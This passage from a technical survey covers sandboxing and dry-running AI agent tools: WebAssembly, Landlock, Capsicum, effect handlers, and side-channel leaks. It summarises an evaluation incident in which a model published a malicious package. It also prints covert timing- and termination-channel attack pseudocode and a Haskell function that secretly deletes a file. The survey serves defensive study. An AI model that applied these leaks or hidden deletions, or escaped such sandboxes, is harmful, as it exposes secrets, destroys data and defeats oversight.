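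`find_invoice` needs to import at least one function, to fetch a record. If the host supplies only that function, a colleague can't add a log line without asking for a second import. This is the same rule as Joe-E's, but it works for a compiled program in any language, without restructuring the source to satisfy a verifier. However, the import list doesn't show what the host's functions do, which could include flagging an invoice as viewed.

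*Certified Purity for Cognitive Workflow Executors* (2026) uses import lists to keep steps in an AI workflow free of effects. The host grants only functions from an approved list of pure ones, so the guarantee is only as reliable as that list. *Beyond Static Endpoints* (2026) instead gives model-written programs a single import, `CALL`, which can request any operation the service offers, so all side effects pass through one place. If a program fails partway and runs again, the host returns the recorded results of completed writes instead of repeating the writes.

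### Directories as handles

Modules that work with files usually import functions from WASI, a standard system interface for WebAssembly. In its first version, a module may import a function for reading files, but can use it only on handles the host supplies at the start and on files inside any directories those handles refer to. The second version has separate imports for files, network, clocks and random numbers, so a reviewer can tell from the compiled program whether it could use the network. In the third version, according to WASI's *Security*, code no longer has to pass a network handle with every operation. The host still decides whether to grant network access, but any code in the program can then use it.

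The import for files covers both reading and writing, so whether a tool is read-only depends on its handles. WASI uses a flag to mark whether a directory handle allows changes. According to the definition quoted in *Clarification on mutate-directory flag* (appcypher, 2024), a program can't use a handle without the flag to create, rename, delete or modify anything, or to obtain another handle that would allow it. The restriction therefore carries over to everything the program opens through the directory, as with a membrane, which prevents the kind of leak that broke the invoice facet.

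In Wasmtime, the host sets each directory to `ReadOnly` or `ReadWrite`. According to Wasmtime's *FsPerms*, `ReadOnly` forbids changing, extending or truncating files, and creating or deleting files, directories and links. These limits work only if the runtime enforces them correctly. OSV's *RUSTSEC-2026-0149* (2026) and RustSec describe two flaws, both since fixed, that let modules bypass Wasmtime's limits on writing files.

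Even printing text can have side effects, because some terminals write files or run commands when they receive special character sequences. Wasmtime replaces these sequences with harmless ones when a module prints to a terminal.

### Agent runtimes built on WebAssembly

Microsoft's *Introducing Wassette* (2025) announced an MCP server that runs each tool as a WebAssembly component and denies access by default. The user grants access in a policy file. For `find_invoice`, the main part might be:

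```
permissions:
  storage:
    allow:
      - uri: "fs://config/billing.yaml"
        access: ["read"]
  network:
    allow:
      - host: "billing.example.com"
```

The tool can read its settings and contact the billing service, but can't write to any file. The storage rule distinguishes reading from writing, but the network rule specifies only a host, so it would allow a request that cancels an invoice. Wassette also has built-in tools for granting more access while it runs, so the policy file describes only the tool's initial permissions.

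Wassette itself logs every call, including the tool's name, how long the call took and whether it succeeded, according to Microsoft's *Frequently Asked Questions (FAQ)*. A call to `find_invoice` would therefore add a log line even if the tool had no way to write one. To adopt Wassette, developers have to rewrite existing MCP servers as components.

Sandboxing tools individually can also leave some of them unsandboxed. The agent system IronClaw runs tools in WebAssembly if the agent calls them directly, but not if it reaches them through an MCP server. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) uses IronClaw as an example and warns that a sandbox no longer gives complete protection if a tool can reach an unrestricted shell or an unsandboxed helper. NemoClaw avoids most of this problem by sandboxing the whole agent.

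The model in the *wasm agent* prototype has no shell. Instead, it writes a Rust program, which one tool compiles to WebAssembly and another runs with access only to the directories that the model names in its request. The log of requests therefore shows every directory the program could have changed, whereas a log of shell commands shows only their text. Each run is also limited to 20 billion instructions by default, which stops endless loops. *wasm agent* treats such a stop as clean, but a program stopped after writing the first of two files leaves that file changed. The prototype also handles large libraries poorly, since they often need to run their own code while being built.

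### Capsicum, Landlock and read-only mounts

Rewriting every tool for WebAssembly isn't practical, so it helps that operating systems can limit ordinary programs too. On Unix-like systems, a program uses an open file, pipe or network connection through a file descriptor, which is a number assigned by the kernel (the core of the operating system). A descriptor works much like a capability, because a program can't gain access by making up a number. But most programs can also open any of their user's files by name.

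Capsicum, a part of FreeBSD, attaches a set of rights to each file descriptor. A new descriptor starts with all of them, and a program can remove rights but never add them back, according to the FreeBSD manual. The kernel checks the rights at every operation, so once a program has given up the right to write, writing through that descriptor fails while reading still works. The program can still open the same file again by name unless it enters capability mode, where it can open files only through directories it already has open. Programs that expect to open files by name usually need changes to run in this mode.

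*Landlock* (Salaün, 2026) describes a Linux mechanism of the same name. A program lists the kinds of access to deny by default, adds exceptions, such as reading anything under `/usr`, and applies the rules to itself. Every process it then starts inherits the limits, and nothing can lift them. An agent product can therefore apply them just before it runs a shell command, without modifying the command.

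Landlock checks a file's path when a program opens it, and doesn't check later reads and writes. If the agent product opened a log for writing before applying the rules and passed the descriptor to a command, the command can still write to the log. The rules also have to deny Landlock's separate right to truncate files, because Linux lets a program open a file for reading and empty it in the same step. As of March 2026, Landlock couldn't stop a program from changing a file's permissions, owner, timestamps or extended attributes. It supports fewer restrictions on older versions of Linux, and Salaün recommends that programs apply whatever the machine supports, so the same tool may be less restricted on an old server.

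A read-only mount closes some of these gaps. Mounting attaches a set of files to the directory tree. If the mount is read-only, the kernel refuses any change made through it, including changes to permissions, owners and timestamps. The same files may still be writable through another mount, but a container, which gives a process its own view of the file system, can leave out the writable mount.

| Mechanism | What it checks | When |
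|---|---|---|
| WebAssembly imports | Whether the host has supplied everything the module needs | Before the module runs |
| WASI read-only directory | Whether the handle allows changes | When the module asks to open or change something |
| Capsicum | The rights on the descriptor | At every operation |
| Landlock | The file's path, or the network port | When the program opens the file or connects |
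| Read-only mount | Whether the mount allows changes | When the program opens a file for writing or changes its details |

### When reading changes something

Reading a file can have side effects even when writes to it are blocked. Many file systems record when somebody last read each file. Linux normally updates this access time if the file has changed since the last recorded read, or if that record is more than a day old. If a cleanup job deletes files that nobody has opened for a month, an agent that searches the whole disk could prevent it from deleting old files. A read-only mount prevents these updates, and so does the `noatime` option on a writable mount.

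Reading from a pipe removes the data, so if an agent reads what one program is sending another, the second program never receives it. Reading a tape moves it forward, and some hardware clears a status value when a program reads it. On Linux, just opening `/dev/watchdog` starts a timer that restarts the machine unless a program keeps resetting it. A read-only mount protects stored files, but it doesn't stop a program from reading, or even writing to, the pipes and devices that have names in the mounted file system.

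A tool can do more damage through a connection to a local service. Many computers run Docker, which starts containers and accepts requests through a socket, a connection point with a name in the file system. A tool that can't write to the disk but can reach this socket could use it to start a container that can. In Miller and Shapiro's terms, the tool would have the authority to write without the permission.

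Landlock couldn't control access to named sockets until Linux 7.1 (Salaün, *Landlock update for v7.1-rc1*, 2026). Linux 7.2 added control over UDP, which sends data without first setting up a connection (Salaün, *Landlock update for v7.2-rc1*, 2026). Earlier versions could restrict TCP connections, but only by port number. A rule that lets `find_invoice` use port 443 for the billing service also lets it contact any other website on that port, and Landlock can't allow requests for an invoice while blocking requests to cancel one.

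### Coarse limits and fine ones

Process limits are much coarser than types. The kernel controls access to files, ports and processes, not to application objects such as invoices. It gives `format_invoice` and `find_invoice` the same access if they run in the same process, while an effect type or a capture set can allow one to use the network and forbid the other. A compiler also reports a forbidden write before the program starts, whereas the kernel refuses it only when the program attempts it, perhaps halfway through a task. WebAssembly falls in between, since a developer can compile each function to its own module and give it imports as narrow as `fetch_record`.

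An effect checker can give the wrong result if `fetch` is mislabeled, but a process without network access can't connect, whatever the label. TACIT's compiler can't control what a command does after the agent's program launches it, but a process limit can. Types and process limits fail for different reasons, so it makes sense to use both. The developer can use types to separate the functions inside a tool, and run the tool in a process that has only the access its least restricted function needs.

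### The command that actually runs

Some agent products decide whether a shell command is read-only by examining its text. This assumes that the text the model wrote is what the computer executes. Suppose an agent on Windows runs this search:

```
findstr "total > 100" invoices.txt
```

Some launchers remove the quotation marks before PowerShell, a Windows shell, interprets the command. PowerShell then treats `>` as an instruction to save the output in a file named `100`, overwriting any existing file with that name, even though the reviewer approved a search. A process limit would block this write because it restricts what the program does, regardless of how the command looked.

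Yang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Do Tool Calls Execute as Intended?*, measured how often such changes happen. They collected 47,828 shell calls that Claude Code and Codex had made on Windows, in 261 sessions by six developers at one company. Rerunning the commands could have caused damage, so they sent each one through the same launch path to a harmless recorder and compared what arrived with what the model had written.

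Of 11,982 calls whose form put them at risk, such as long commands or ones with certain quotes and backslashes, 1,199 had changed. That is 10.0% of the calls at risk and about 2.5% of all calls. The rate for Claude Code's Bash tool was 12.0% of 7,491 calls at risk. Its most worrying fault was merging pairs of backslashes. In 535 of 663 such cases, the altered command ran without any reported error, so nothing prompted the model or the user to check it.

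The 10% figure may be high for other users. Among 657 at-risk Windows calls from two developers outside the company, only 7 were changed. On Linux, products that passed the command to the shell as a single argument delivered it intact every time, including in 161,214 Codex calls from the outside developers. Products that typed the command into a terminal or rewrote it first altered some commands. Yang and colleagues also counted any change of meaning, and most of these changes probably didn't turn a read into a write.

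Yang and colleagues found that 10 of the 22 MCP servers they tested also altered calls. On Windows, one file server received the name `a:b`, wrote to a hidden stream attached to the file `a`, and reported success. The researchers' repair tool, INTACT, puts a command in a file or encodes it so that the launcher can't reinterpret it, and blocks any command it can't deliver unchanged.

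## Dry runs by replacing effect handlers

A process limit stops a program at its first forbidden write. Someone who wants to see everything the program would do needs a dry run, in which the program continues past each write as though the write had happened. Developers often implement dry runs as an option that every function has to handle, which is easy to get wrong. Tan and colleagues cite a 2024 report from a user of aider, an open-source coding agent, who wanted a patch to review. The option for showing changes also applied them, and adding the dry-run option produced no patch.

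With effect handlers, a program requests side effects by name instead of carrying them out itself, and a separate piece of code, the handler, determines what each request does. A developer can turn a real run into a dry run by replacing the handler, without editing the program.

### Operations, handlers and the rest of the program

In the early 2000s, Gordon Plotkin and John Power proposed describing effects by the operations that cause them, such as reading or writing memory, and the equations those operations obey. One equation for memory is that a read straight after a write returns what the program wrote. Effects that fit this description are called algebraic. In *Handling Algebraic Effects*, Plotkin and Pretnar (2013) sum up the idea by saying that a computation either returns a value or performs an operation whose outcome determines how the computation continues.

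Raising an exception fits this scheme, but catching one doesn't. Choosing at random between two refunds and then logging the result is the same as choosing between two programs that each make one refund and log it. But moving the logging inside a `catch` block that comes before it changes which errors the block catches. Plotkin and Pretnar therefore treated catching as giving a new meaning to the operation that raises the exception, and let programmers do the same for every other operation.

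An exception handler receives the error, and the rest of the program never runs. A general effect handler receives the operation's arguments and also the rest of the program, as a function `k`. If the handler calls `k` with a value, the program continues as if the operation had returned that value. In a notation close to that of Tan and colleagues, the rule is:

```
handle E[perform op(v)] with h   →   body,  with x = v
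                                     and   k = (z ↦ handle E[z] with h)

where h contains the clause  op(x; k) ⇒ body
and no handler inside E deals with op
```

`E` is the program around the request, with a gap where the result will go. The last condition means the nearest suitable handler gets the request. Calling `k` fills the gap and continues under the same handler, so later requests reach `h` too. The body of the clause runs outside `h`, so requests it makes go to handlers further out. When the program finishes with a value, `handle v with h` becomes `v`.

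*Programming with Algebraic Effects and Handlers* (Bauer and Pretnar, 2012) presents Eff, a language built on these ideas. A request that no handler deals with passes outward to the top level of the program, where a built-in default does the real reading or writing for standard input and output.

### One program under two handlers

This program reads an invoice, requests a refund and reports it:

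```
invoice = perform find_invoice(1042)
number  = perform refund(invoice.id, invoice.amount)
perform report("Refunded, number " + number)
```

A live handler and a dry-run handler for it might look like this:

```
live = handler {
    find_invoice(id; k)    ⇒ k(billing.fetch(id))
    refund(id, amount; k)  ⇒ k(billing.refund(id, amount))
    report(text; k)        ⇒ k(screen.show(text))
}

dry = handler {
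    find_invoice(id; k)    ⇒ k(billing.fetch(id))
    refund(id, amount; k)  ⇒ planned.add(id, amount); k("DRY-1")
    report(text; k)        ⇒ k(screen.show("Preview: " + text))
}
```

If invoice 1042 is for $100, the two runs go as follows:

| Request | What is left in `k` | Under `live` | Under `dry` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `find_invoice(1042)` | The refund and the report | Fetches the invoice and resumes with it | The same |
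| `refund(1042, 100)` | The report | Sends the refund and resumes with the service's number, say `R-77` | Adds the refund to a list and resumes with `DRY-1` |
| `report(...)` | Nothing | Shows "Refunded, number R-77" | Shows "Preview: Refunded, number DRY-1" |

Applying the rule to the refund in the dry run gives these steps:

```
handle (number = perform refund(1042, 100);
        perform report("Refunded, number " + number)) with dry

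→   planned.add(1042, 100); k("DRY-1")

→   handle (number = "DRY-1";
            perform report("Refunded, number " + number)) with dry
```

At the end, the list contains one planned refund and no money has moved. But the dry run actually fetched the invoice, so if the billing service marks fetched invoices as viewed, this one is now marked.

A handler doesn't have to call `k` exactly once. If it never calls `k`, the program stops at the first refund, as it would after an exception. A handler could also call `k` twice, once with a refund number and once with an error, to show the user what the program would do in either case. Plotkin and Pretnar describe a handler of this kind, which follows both branches of every choice in a program and collects the results in a list. The number of runs grows quickly, since ten requests with two possible outcomes each can lead to 1,024 runs. Any operation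 the handler still performs for real may also happen many times.

Some of their other handlers are already simple dry runs. One works like the Unix device `/dev/null`, discarding everything a process writes to standard output and letting the process continue. Another lets a set number of characters through and suppresses the rest.

### Free monads and injected interpreters

Programmers can get much the same result in languages without effect handlers. In Haskell, they can represent the program as data:

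```
data Program a
  = Done a
  | FindInvoice Id        (Invoice -> Program a)
  | Refund      Id Amount (Number  -> Program a)
  | Report      Text      (()      -> Program a)
```

A `Program` is either finished or made up of a request and a function, playing the role of `k`, that takes the request's result and returns the rest of the program. An interpreter is an ordinary function that acts on the first request, passes a result to the stored function, and repeats until it reaches `Done`. An interpreter that sends refunds can be replaced with one that only records them.

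This construction is a free monad, called "free" because it stores the requests without giving them any meaning. *What is algebraic about algebraic effects and handlers?* (2018) explains the mathematics behind the resemblance. Computations are the elements of a free model of the operations, and handlers are structure-preserving maps out of that model. If the operations obey no equations, the free model consists of trees of requests like the ones above.

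A simpler method is to pass the interpreter to the program as an argument. In Python:

```
def refund_invoice(services, id):
    invoice = services.find_invoice(id)
    number = services.refund(invoice.id, invoice.amount)
    services.report("Refunded, number " + number)
```

The caller supplies either a live `services` object or one that only records refunds. This looks just like the object-capability style. An ordinary method can return a value or raise an error, but unlike an effect handler, it doesn't receive the continuation `k`, so it can't run the rest of the program twice.

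*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which presents a small formal language for AI agents, treats the language model this way. Its interpreter takes a function that supplies the model's answers in order. In live runs, this function queries a real model. The interpreter also returns the answers it used, which a developer could feed back in to repeat the run.

*Composable Effect Handling for Programming LLM-integrated Scripts* (Wang, 2025) brings effect handlers to ordinary Python. One example script asks a language model for topics in a research field and then for a description of each. Without changing the script, the developer can wrap it in handlers that send its requests to a real model or in handlers that answer them from a recording.

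Wang also used handlers to speed up a script that searches for ways to make 24 out of four numbers. Three puzzles took between 34 and 37 seconds each with a handler that sent many requests to the model at once, and between 413 and 465 seconds each with one that sent requests one at a time. (Wang gives the average speedup as 10.88 times, but the three timings work out at 11 to 13 times.) The gain comes from running requests in parallel, which a programmer could also do by hand, but handlers make it possible without rewriting the search.

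### How ETAS keeps track of previewed writes

In the main example for ETAS, Tan and colleagues' language for agents, a reviewer agent reads source files and proposes a patch. The program then asks a person for approval and applies the patch. One line defines the dry run:

```
let DryRun = handler { Repo.apply(p) ⇒ { resume; } };
```

Here `resume` calls `k`, so the program continues without writing anything. `DryRun` doesn't handle the approval request, so the request still goes to a real person during a preview. A handler in ETAS can resume at most once per request, so it can't explore several outcomes.

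In an ordinary effect system, handling an operation removes it from the program's effect type:

```
effects of (handle e with h)  =  (effects of e, minus the operations h handles)
                                 ∪  effects of h's own clauses
```

This is accurate, because the program can't change the repository under `DryRun`. But a dry run should also reveal whether the program breaks the rules. Suppose a colleague deletes the approval step. Under `DryRun`, the effect type doesn't include the write, so checking the type for unapproved writes finds nothing. The type also doesn't record order, so checking it can't catch a program that asks for approval only after writing.

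ETAS therefore keeps a second record, a summary of the requests a function may make and the order in which it may make them. Handling a write removes it from the effect type but not from the summary:

| Version of the workflow | Effect type | Request summary | Approval before every write? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Approval, then write | approval, write | approval, then perhaps write | Yes |
| The same, under `DryRun` | approval | approval, then perhaps write | Yes |
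| Write with no approval, under `DryRun` | none | write | No |
| Write, then approval, under `DryRun` | approval | write, then approval | No |

The second and fourth versions have the same effect type, but only one of them follows the rule.

If a handler makes requests of its own, the compiler must assume that they can occur at any point in the sequence and any number of times. It must also assume that the sequence can stop early, because a handler may abandon the program. Tan and colleagues write this as `pref(A ∥ A_h*)`, where `A` is the program's summary and `A_h` is the handler's. The symbol `∥` interleaves the two, `*` repeats the handler's part, and `pref` adds every incomplete run.

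Developers write rules about these summaries. `ReviewOnly` lets the reviewer query the model and read files but forbids writes, including previewed ones. `ApprovedApply` requires an approval request before any write request. The compiler turns each rule into a small state machine, which for `ApprovedApply` is:

| Current state | After an approval request | After a write request |
|---|---|---|
| No approval requested yet | Approval requested | Rule broken |
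| Approval requested | No change | No change |

The compiler runs every sequence in the summary through the machine. It accepts the program if they all follow the rule and rejects it if they all break the rule. If only some break it, the compiler lets the program run, but the machine checks each request before it reaches a handler or the real system.

`ApprovedApply` is a weak rule because it allows any number of writes after a single approval request, even if the person said no. An `if` statement in the program checks the person's answer. The host, the trusted software that carries out real operations, separately checks permissions and whether the person consented to this particular patch. In a dry run, the handler intercepts the write before it reaches the host, so the preview can show a write that the host would have refused.

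### The tests of ETAS

Tan and colleagues wrote a coding agent called Nomo in ETAS and tested the part that decides which files to read or search. Handlers supplied prepared answers in place of the model and the file system. In ten test scenarios, four runs finished normally and six stopped where they were supposed to. The handlers dealt correctly with all 19 requests: 12 to the model, 5 to read files and 2 to search. None of these requests was a write, so the test supports using handlers to replace a model and a file system but provides no evidence about previewing changes.

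The order rules got a separate test with six small programs, which Tan and colleagues compiled but didn't run. The compiler accepted the two correct ones, which requested approval before writing, with and without `DryRun`. It rejected the other four:

- a program that never requested approval
- a program that requested approval after the write
- a read-only program with a write that a handler intercepted
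- a program with an unhandled write that its effect type didn't declare

These tests are tiny, and the language's designers wrote all of them. They show that the compiler works on the intended cases, but not how well it would work on an agent written by someone else. Only one of the six programs has a handled write that breaks a rule, which is the case ETAS's summaries are meant to catch.

Tan and colleagues tested the state machines more thoroughly. They wrote a separate Python version and compared its verdicts with those from checking 384 rules directly, using every sequence of up to six requests. The verdicts agreed in all 419,712 comparisons, though the sequences contained only three kinds of request.

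### When the handler has to invent a result

`DryRun` is simple partly because applying a patch returns nothing. A refund returns a number, might fail, and changes what later reads should return. Suppose the refund program also checks that the refund went through:

```
number = perform refund(1042, 100)
status = perform get_status(1042)
if status == "refunded":
    perform report("Refunded, number " + number)
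else:
    perform refund(1042, 100)      # try again
```

`get_status` queries the billing service directly because the cache might be stale. If a dry run records the refund but passes `get_status` through to the real service, the service correctly returns "paid". The program then requests a second refund, which a real run might never do. This dry run violates the equation that a read after a write returns what the program wrote.

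Plotkin and Pretnar's rollback handler avoids the problem for a single memory location. While the program runs, the handler leaves the memory unchanged and keeps the latest value separately. Writes replace this value and reads return it. The handler copies the final value to memory only if the program finishes without raising an exception. A dry-run handler could work the same way but omit the final copy. For the refund program, it would record that invoice 1042 has a pending refund and return "refunded".

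But then the handler's author has to know how the billing service behaves. Suppose it holds refunds of $100 or more for review and reports their status as "in review":

| Run | Answer to `get_status` | What the program does next | Refunds requested |
|---|---|---|---|
| Dry run that reads the live status | paid | Tries again | 2 |
| Dry run that remembers the refund | refunded | Reports success | 1 |
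| Real run, if the service pays at once | refunded | Reports success | 1 |
| Real run, if the service holds the refund | in review | Tries again | 2 |

With the more careful dry run, the user approves one refund, but the program then requests two because the preview was based on a rule that the service doesn't follow.

In Plotkin and Pretnar's theory, handling a program has no meaning if the handler violates the equations, and there may be no general procedure for deciding whether a handler obeys them. The equations for memory are known, but a billing service rarely comes with a complete list of rules, so a developer has to rely on documentation or experiment.

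Wang, Niu and colleagues (2026), in *MCP-Persona*, measured how much difference experimenting makes. They built simulated versions of personal and workplace apps for testing agents. For the workplace app Lark, they compared two simulators against 50 recorded calls, half of which had succeeded. Each simulator started from the same state as the real call:

| Simulator based on | Agreed on success or failure | Real successes it rejected | Real failures it accepted |
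|---|---|---|---|
| Documentation only | 29 of 50 (58%) | 13 of 25 | 8 of 25 |
| Observed calls to the real app | 47 of 50 (94%) | 2 of 25 | 1 of 25 |

The simulator based on documentation was right little more than half the time. Errors add up over a long task, and even a simulator with 94% accuracy would get ten calls in a row right only about 54% of the time if its errors were independent. Wang and colleagues also had to observe the app's behaviour by making real calls with test accounts, which isn't possible for every service.

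A language model can generate the tool results instead. The benchmark in *Evaluating LLMs as Agentic Workflow Executors in Real-World Customer Support Skills* (2026) does this for 281 tools, because fixed answers can't reflect a customer's situation or earlier steps, and live tools could change real customer data. The model's answers follow the format of the real tools, but the real service might have answered differently.

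If a language model chooses the calls, the real run may differ from the dry run even when the simulated results are accurate, because the model may make different choices the second time. Replaying the model's recorded answers prevents this, but those answers may no longer make sense if a tool returns something different in the real run.

### Effects that bypass the handler

A dry run is safe only if the handler intercepts every effect that matters. In Eff, a request that the handler doesn't cover passes outward to the default, which may carry it out for real. Eff's types don't record effects, so the compiler gives no warning. In ETAS, by contrast, an unhandled write stays in the effect type, and the compiler rejects the program if its declared type doesn't allow writes.

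Neither language can intercept an effect that never becomes a request. Tan and colleagues' proofs assume that every real effect goes through ETAS's operations and that the host's functions report everything they do. Python doesn't enforce either condition. Wang's number-puzzle script prints its results with Python's `print` function, which isn't one of the script's operations, so replacing the handlers doesn't stop the printing. Printing is harmless here, but a direct call to delete a file would bypass the handlers in the same way.

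Telling a model that it is in a simulation does not intercept its tool calls. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes tests in which the prompt stated that Claude had no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left the internet reachable. In one test, Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious package to the public index of Python software, and 15 real systems downloaded and ran it.

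A developer can guard against effects the handler misses by doing the dry run in a process that can't write to files and uses a billing account that can't issue refunds. If the program bypasses the handler, any refund it attempts will fail.

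## Logs, caches, timing, resource use and unsafe escape hatches

A function that a compiler has certified as pure may still need to run in a process without write access. The Haskell type of `format_invoice`, for example, lists no side effects, but a function with this type can print a message, use up the machine's memory, run forever, or reveal a secret through how long it takes. With an escape hatch, it can also delete files.

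| What the function does | Why it still passes the check |
|---|---|
| Prints a debugging message | The language's designers left debugging output out of the type |
| Fills the memory, runs forever or throws an exception | Haskell's designers left these out too, though Koka has labels for exceptions and non-termination |
| Takes longer for some inputs, uses more energy or changes the processor's cache | The checker has no model of the hardware |
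| Makes a later call faster by saving an answer | The type may list the write to the cache, but not its effect on timing |
| Calls `unsafePerformIO`, a mislabelled foreign function or faulty code marked `@assumeSafe` | A programmer told the checker to accept the code |

### Effects that designers leave out of the type

Haskell's debugging function `trace :: String -> a -> a` prints its first argument and returns its second. A developer can therefore add a message to `format_invoice` without changing its type or the types of its callers. But the compiler treats the function as pure, so it may delay a call, merge two identical calls, or skip a call whose result nobody uses. Messages may be out of order or missing, which makes `trace` a poor way to keep an audit log.

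Even one log line per call can do harm. Suppose `find_invoice` logs the whole record, about 2 kilobytes, and agents call it 50 times a second. The log grows by 8.6 gigabytes a day and fills a 100-gigabyte disk in under 12 days. If the billing database is on the same disk, the database can't save payments once the disk is full.

A log line can also trigger other software. An operator might have a rule that blocks an account after a hundred "invoice not found" messages in a minute, so an agent that guesses invoice numbers could lock its own user out. Logging a customer's name and address also creates a second copy of them. More employees may be able to read the log than the billing records, and deleting the customer's account won't delete the log line.

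These guarantees also don't cover memory use. Suppose `format_invoice` pads its text to a width specified in the invoice, and an attacker sends an invoice with a width of ten billion characters. The function only computes, but it may exhaust the machine's memory, and the operating system may stop another program to free space.

*Safe Haskell* (Terei, Mazières and colleagues) accepts the loose definition of purity that Leijen described, under which a pure function may throw an exception or never return. This is reasonable because no compiler can determine for every program whether it will finish, and Odersky and colleagues point out that even dividing by zero can cause an exception. TACIT therefore handles exceptions at run time. An agent's function returns a `Try` value, which contains either a result or the error. If the function was processing a secret, the program can wrap the error too,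 so the agent learns nothing from it.

### How a cache reveals a lookup

Suppose everyone in a finance department shares one copy of `find_invoice`. A lookup takes 1 millisecond if the record is in the cache and 50 milliseconds if the tool has to fetch it. Bob wants to know whether Alice, an auditor, is looking into invoice 1042. He first looks up invoice 2000, which puts that record in the cache. An hour later he looks up invoice 1042 and times the call:

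| What Alice did during that hour | Record in the cache | Time for Bob's call |
|---|---|---|
| Looked up invoice 1042 | 1042 | 1 ms |
| Looked up another invoice last | The other invoice | 50 ms |
| Nothing | 2000 | 50 ms |

If the call takes 1 millisecond, Bob knows that somebody looked up invoice 1042. If he looks up invoice 2000 again instead, he learns whether anybody has looked up a different invoice. With a cache that kept thousands of records, he could check 20 invoices within a second. Every call returns the correct record, and an effect type would list only a harmless-looking write to the cache.

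The developer could close this leak by making every answer take 50 milliseconds. If nine lookups in ten normally come from the cache, that raises the average time from 5.9 to 50 milliseconds and makes the cache pointless. Giving each user a separate cache is better, but it takes more memory, and fewer lookups find their record already saved.

Cloud customers who share hardware are also exposed to timing leaks. In *Plugging Side-Channel Leaks with Timing Information Flow Control*, Ford (2012) notes that reserving hardware for each customer would close these leaks but give up the efficiency of sharing. Ford proposes labels that record what the timing of an event might reveal, along with queues that release results at a controlled pace.

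### Termination and timing leaks in LIO

LIO, the library that supplied the policies in ELBA's AgentDojo tests, was open to similar attacks. It stops a program from writing anything public after the program has read a secret. An early version also had a function, `toLabeled`, that let a program process a secret in a separate block, get the result back in a wrapper, and then continue with public work. Stefan, Russo and colleagues (2012), in *Addressing Covert Termination and Timing Channels in Concurrent Information Flow Systems*, showed how a program could abuse this. In simplified form, their first attack is:

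```
for guess in 0, 1, 2, ...:
    toLabeled:
        if secret == guess: loop forever
    print("It is not " + guess)
```

If the secret is 4, the program prints that it is not 0, 1, 2 or 3, and then stops printing. None of the printed lines uses the secret, but anyone who knows the code can work out the secret from them. Revealing a 16-bit number this way can take up to 65,536 rounds. If the program can start several threads, it can give each bit its own thread and reveal the number with only 16 threads.

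A second attack uses the order of two outputs. One thread checks a guess against the secret, waits five seconds if the guess is right, and then writes a line. Another thread always writes its line after three seconds. If the second thread's line comes first, the guess was right. This attack works without a clock. An outsider who has one can use a simpler attack, in which the program delays its reply if the guess is right.

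Stefan and colleagues replaced `toLabeled` with two functions. `forkLIO` starts the secret work in a new thread, and the rest of the program continues immediately. To get the result, the program has to call `waitLIO`, which first marks the program as having read a secret. The program then can't write anything public, so its public output can't depend on whether or when the secret work finished. They proved that this closes the leak through termination.

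This doesn't stop an outsider from learning something by timing the replies, so another component releases them on a schedule, for example one every millisecond. If the program misses a deadline, the interval doubles to 2 milliseconds. An observer can learn something from each doubling, but doublings become rarer as the interval grows.

They tested the attacks on a small dating website that ran other people's apps. Each attack tried to find out who was interested in whom among ten users. The thesis Buiras (2016), in *Securing functional programs with floating-label information-flow control*, which includes this work, gives the results:

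| Attack | Time to recover all ten entries | After the fix |
|---|---|---|
| Loop forever on a correct guess | 73 seconds | No longer possible |
| Change the order of two outputs | 67 seconds | No longer possible |
| Delay the reply | 33 seconds | 3 of 10 entries leaked in 64 seconds, and recovering the rest was infeasible |

Starting a thread added no noticeable time in a small benchmark, and Stefan and colleagues report that the schedule didn't slow well-behaved apps. The larger burden is on programmers, who have to rearrange their code so that nothing public waits for secret work. Somebody trustworthy also has to decide which outputs need a schedule. The test was tiny, but it shows clearly that the original leaks were practical and that the schedule reduces the third leak without removing it.

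A function can leak this way without any malicious code. Stefan and colleagues also repeated a known attack on an old version of OpenSSL, a widely used encryption library. Decryption is close to a pure function, but its running time varied slightly with the key, and these differences revealed the bits of a secret prime behind a 512-bit test key.

### Leaks through the processor's cache

LIO's new functions protect only resources that a Haskell program can name. A processor also keeps recently used data in a small, fast memory of its own, which all the threads on it share. A later chapter of Buiras's thesis, written with Stefan and others, describes an attack that uses this cache:

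1. The program reads a public list, which puts the list in the processor's cache.
2. If a secret bit is 1, a thread fills the cache with other data. If the bit is 0, it does nothing.
3. A second thread reads the public list again and writes a line. This takes longer if the list is no longer in the cache.
4. A third thread writes its line after a fixed number of steps.

The order of the two lines reveals the bit. The attack leaked only 0.75 bits a second, enough to find all the collaborators on a private project on the code-hosting site GitStar in less than a minute.

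The attack works because the computer normally switches threads after a fixed time, and a thread completes fewer instructions in that time when it has to wait for memory. The researchers changed Haskell to switch threads after a fixed number of instructions instead, so the order of the lines no longer depended on the cache. On their machine, about 37 million instructions corresponded to the usual 10 milliseconds. Most test programs ran as fast as before and a few took about 1% longer, but a badly chosen instruction count could double the running time.

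This fix works only if all the threads share one processor core, and it doesn't affect what an outsider can learn with a clock. Clearing the cache at every thread switch would also stop the attack, but the system switched hundreds of times a second, and the researchers judged the slowdown too great.

TACIT does not prevent timing leaks, so an agent's program could reveal one bit of a secret by taking longer for some values than for others. At one bit per second, it could leak a 128-bit key in just over two minutes.

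### Code that the checker accepts on a programmer's word

Haskell's `unsafePerformIO` has the type `IO a -> a`. It takes a computation that may do anything and presents the result as an ordinary value:

```
formatInvoice :: Invoice -> String
formatInvoice inv =
    unsafePerformIO (removeFile "ledger.db" >> return (show inv))
```

This function deletes a file, but its type looks pure. Even reading through `unsafePerformIO` can cause strange results. In an example from Terei and colleagues, a function `f` secretly adds the current time in microseconds to its argument. The compiler is entitled to treat these two expressions as equal:

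```
let x = f 3 in x + x
f 3 + f 3
```

The first reads the clock once and always gives an even number. The second may read the clock twice and give an odd one.

Haskell has this function because some code is pure from the outside but needs side effects internally. For example, the `ByteString` library writes text directly into blocks of memory, though its users see only text that never changes. This is much faster than using Haskell's ordinary strings.

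Calls to code in other languages need similar trust. A programmer can import C's sine function into Haskell with a pure type, and the compiler can't check whether the C code also writes to a file. Scala's `@assumeSafe`, which exempts a library module from safe mode, also relies on the author being right that the module is safe.

### Safe Haskell

Safe Haskell, which Terei and colleagues added to Haskell's main compiler, GHC, keeps code like this away from programs that shouldn't use it. ELBA relies on it to stop an agent's program from calling `unsafePerformIO`. Safe Haskell divides modules, the files that make up a program, into these classes:

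| Class | Meaning | Can a Safe module import it? |
|---|---|---|
| Safe | The compiler has checked that it uses no unsafe features and imports only trusted modules | Yes |
| Trustworthy | It may use unsafe features, but its author promises that others can use it safely | Yes, if the user trusts its package |
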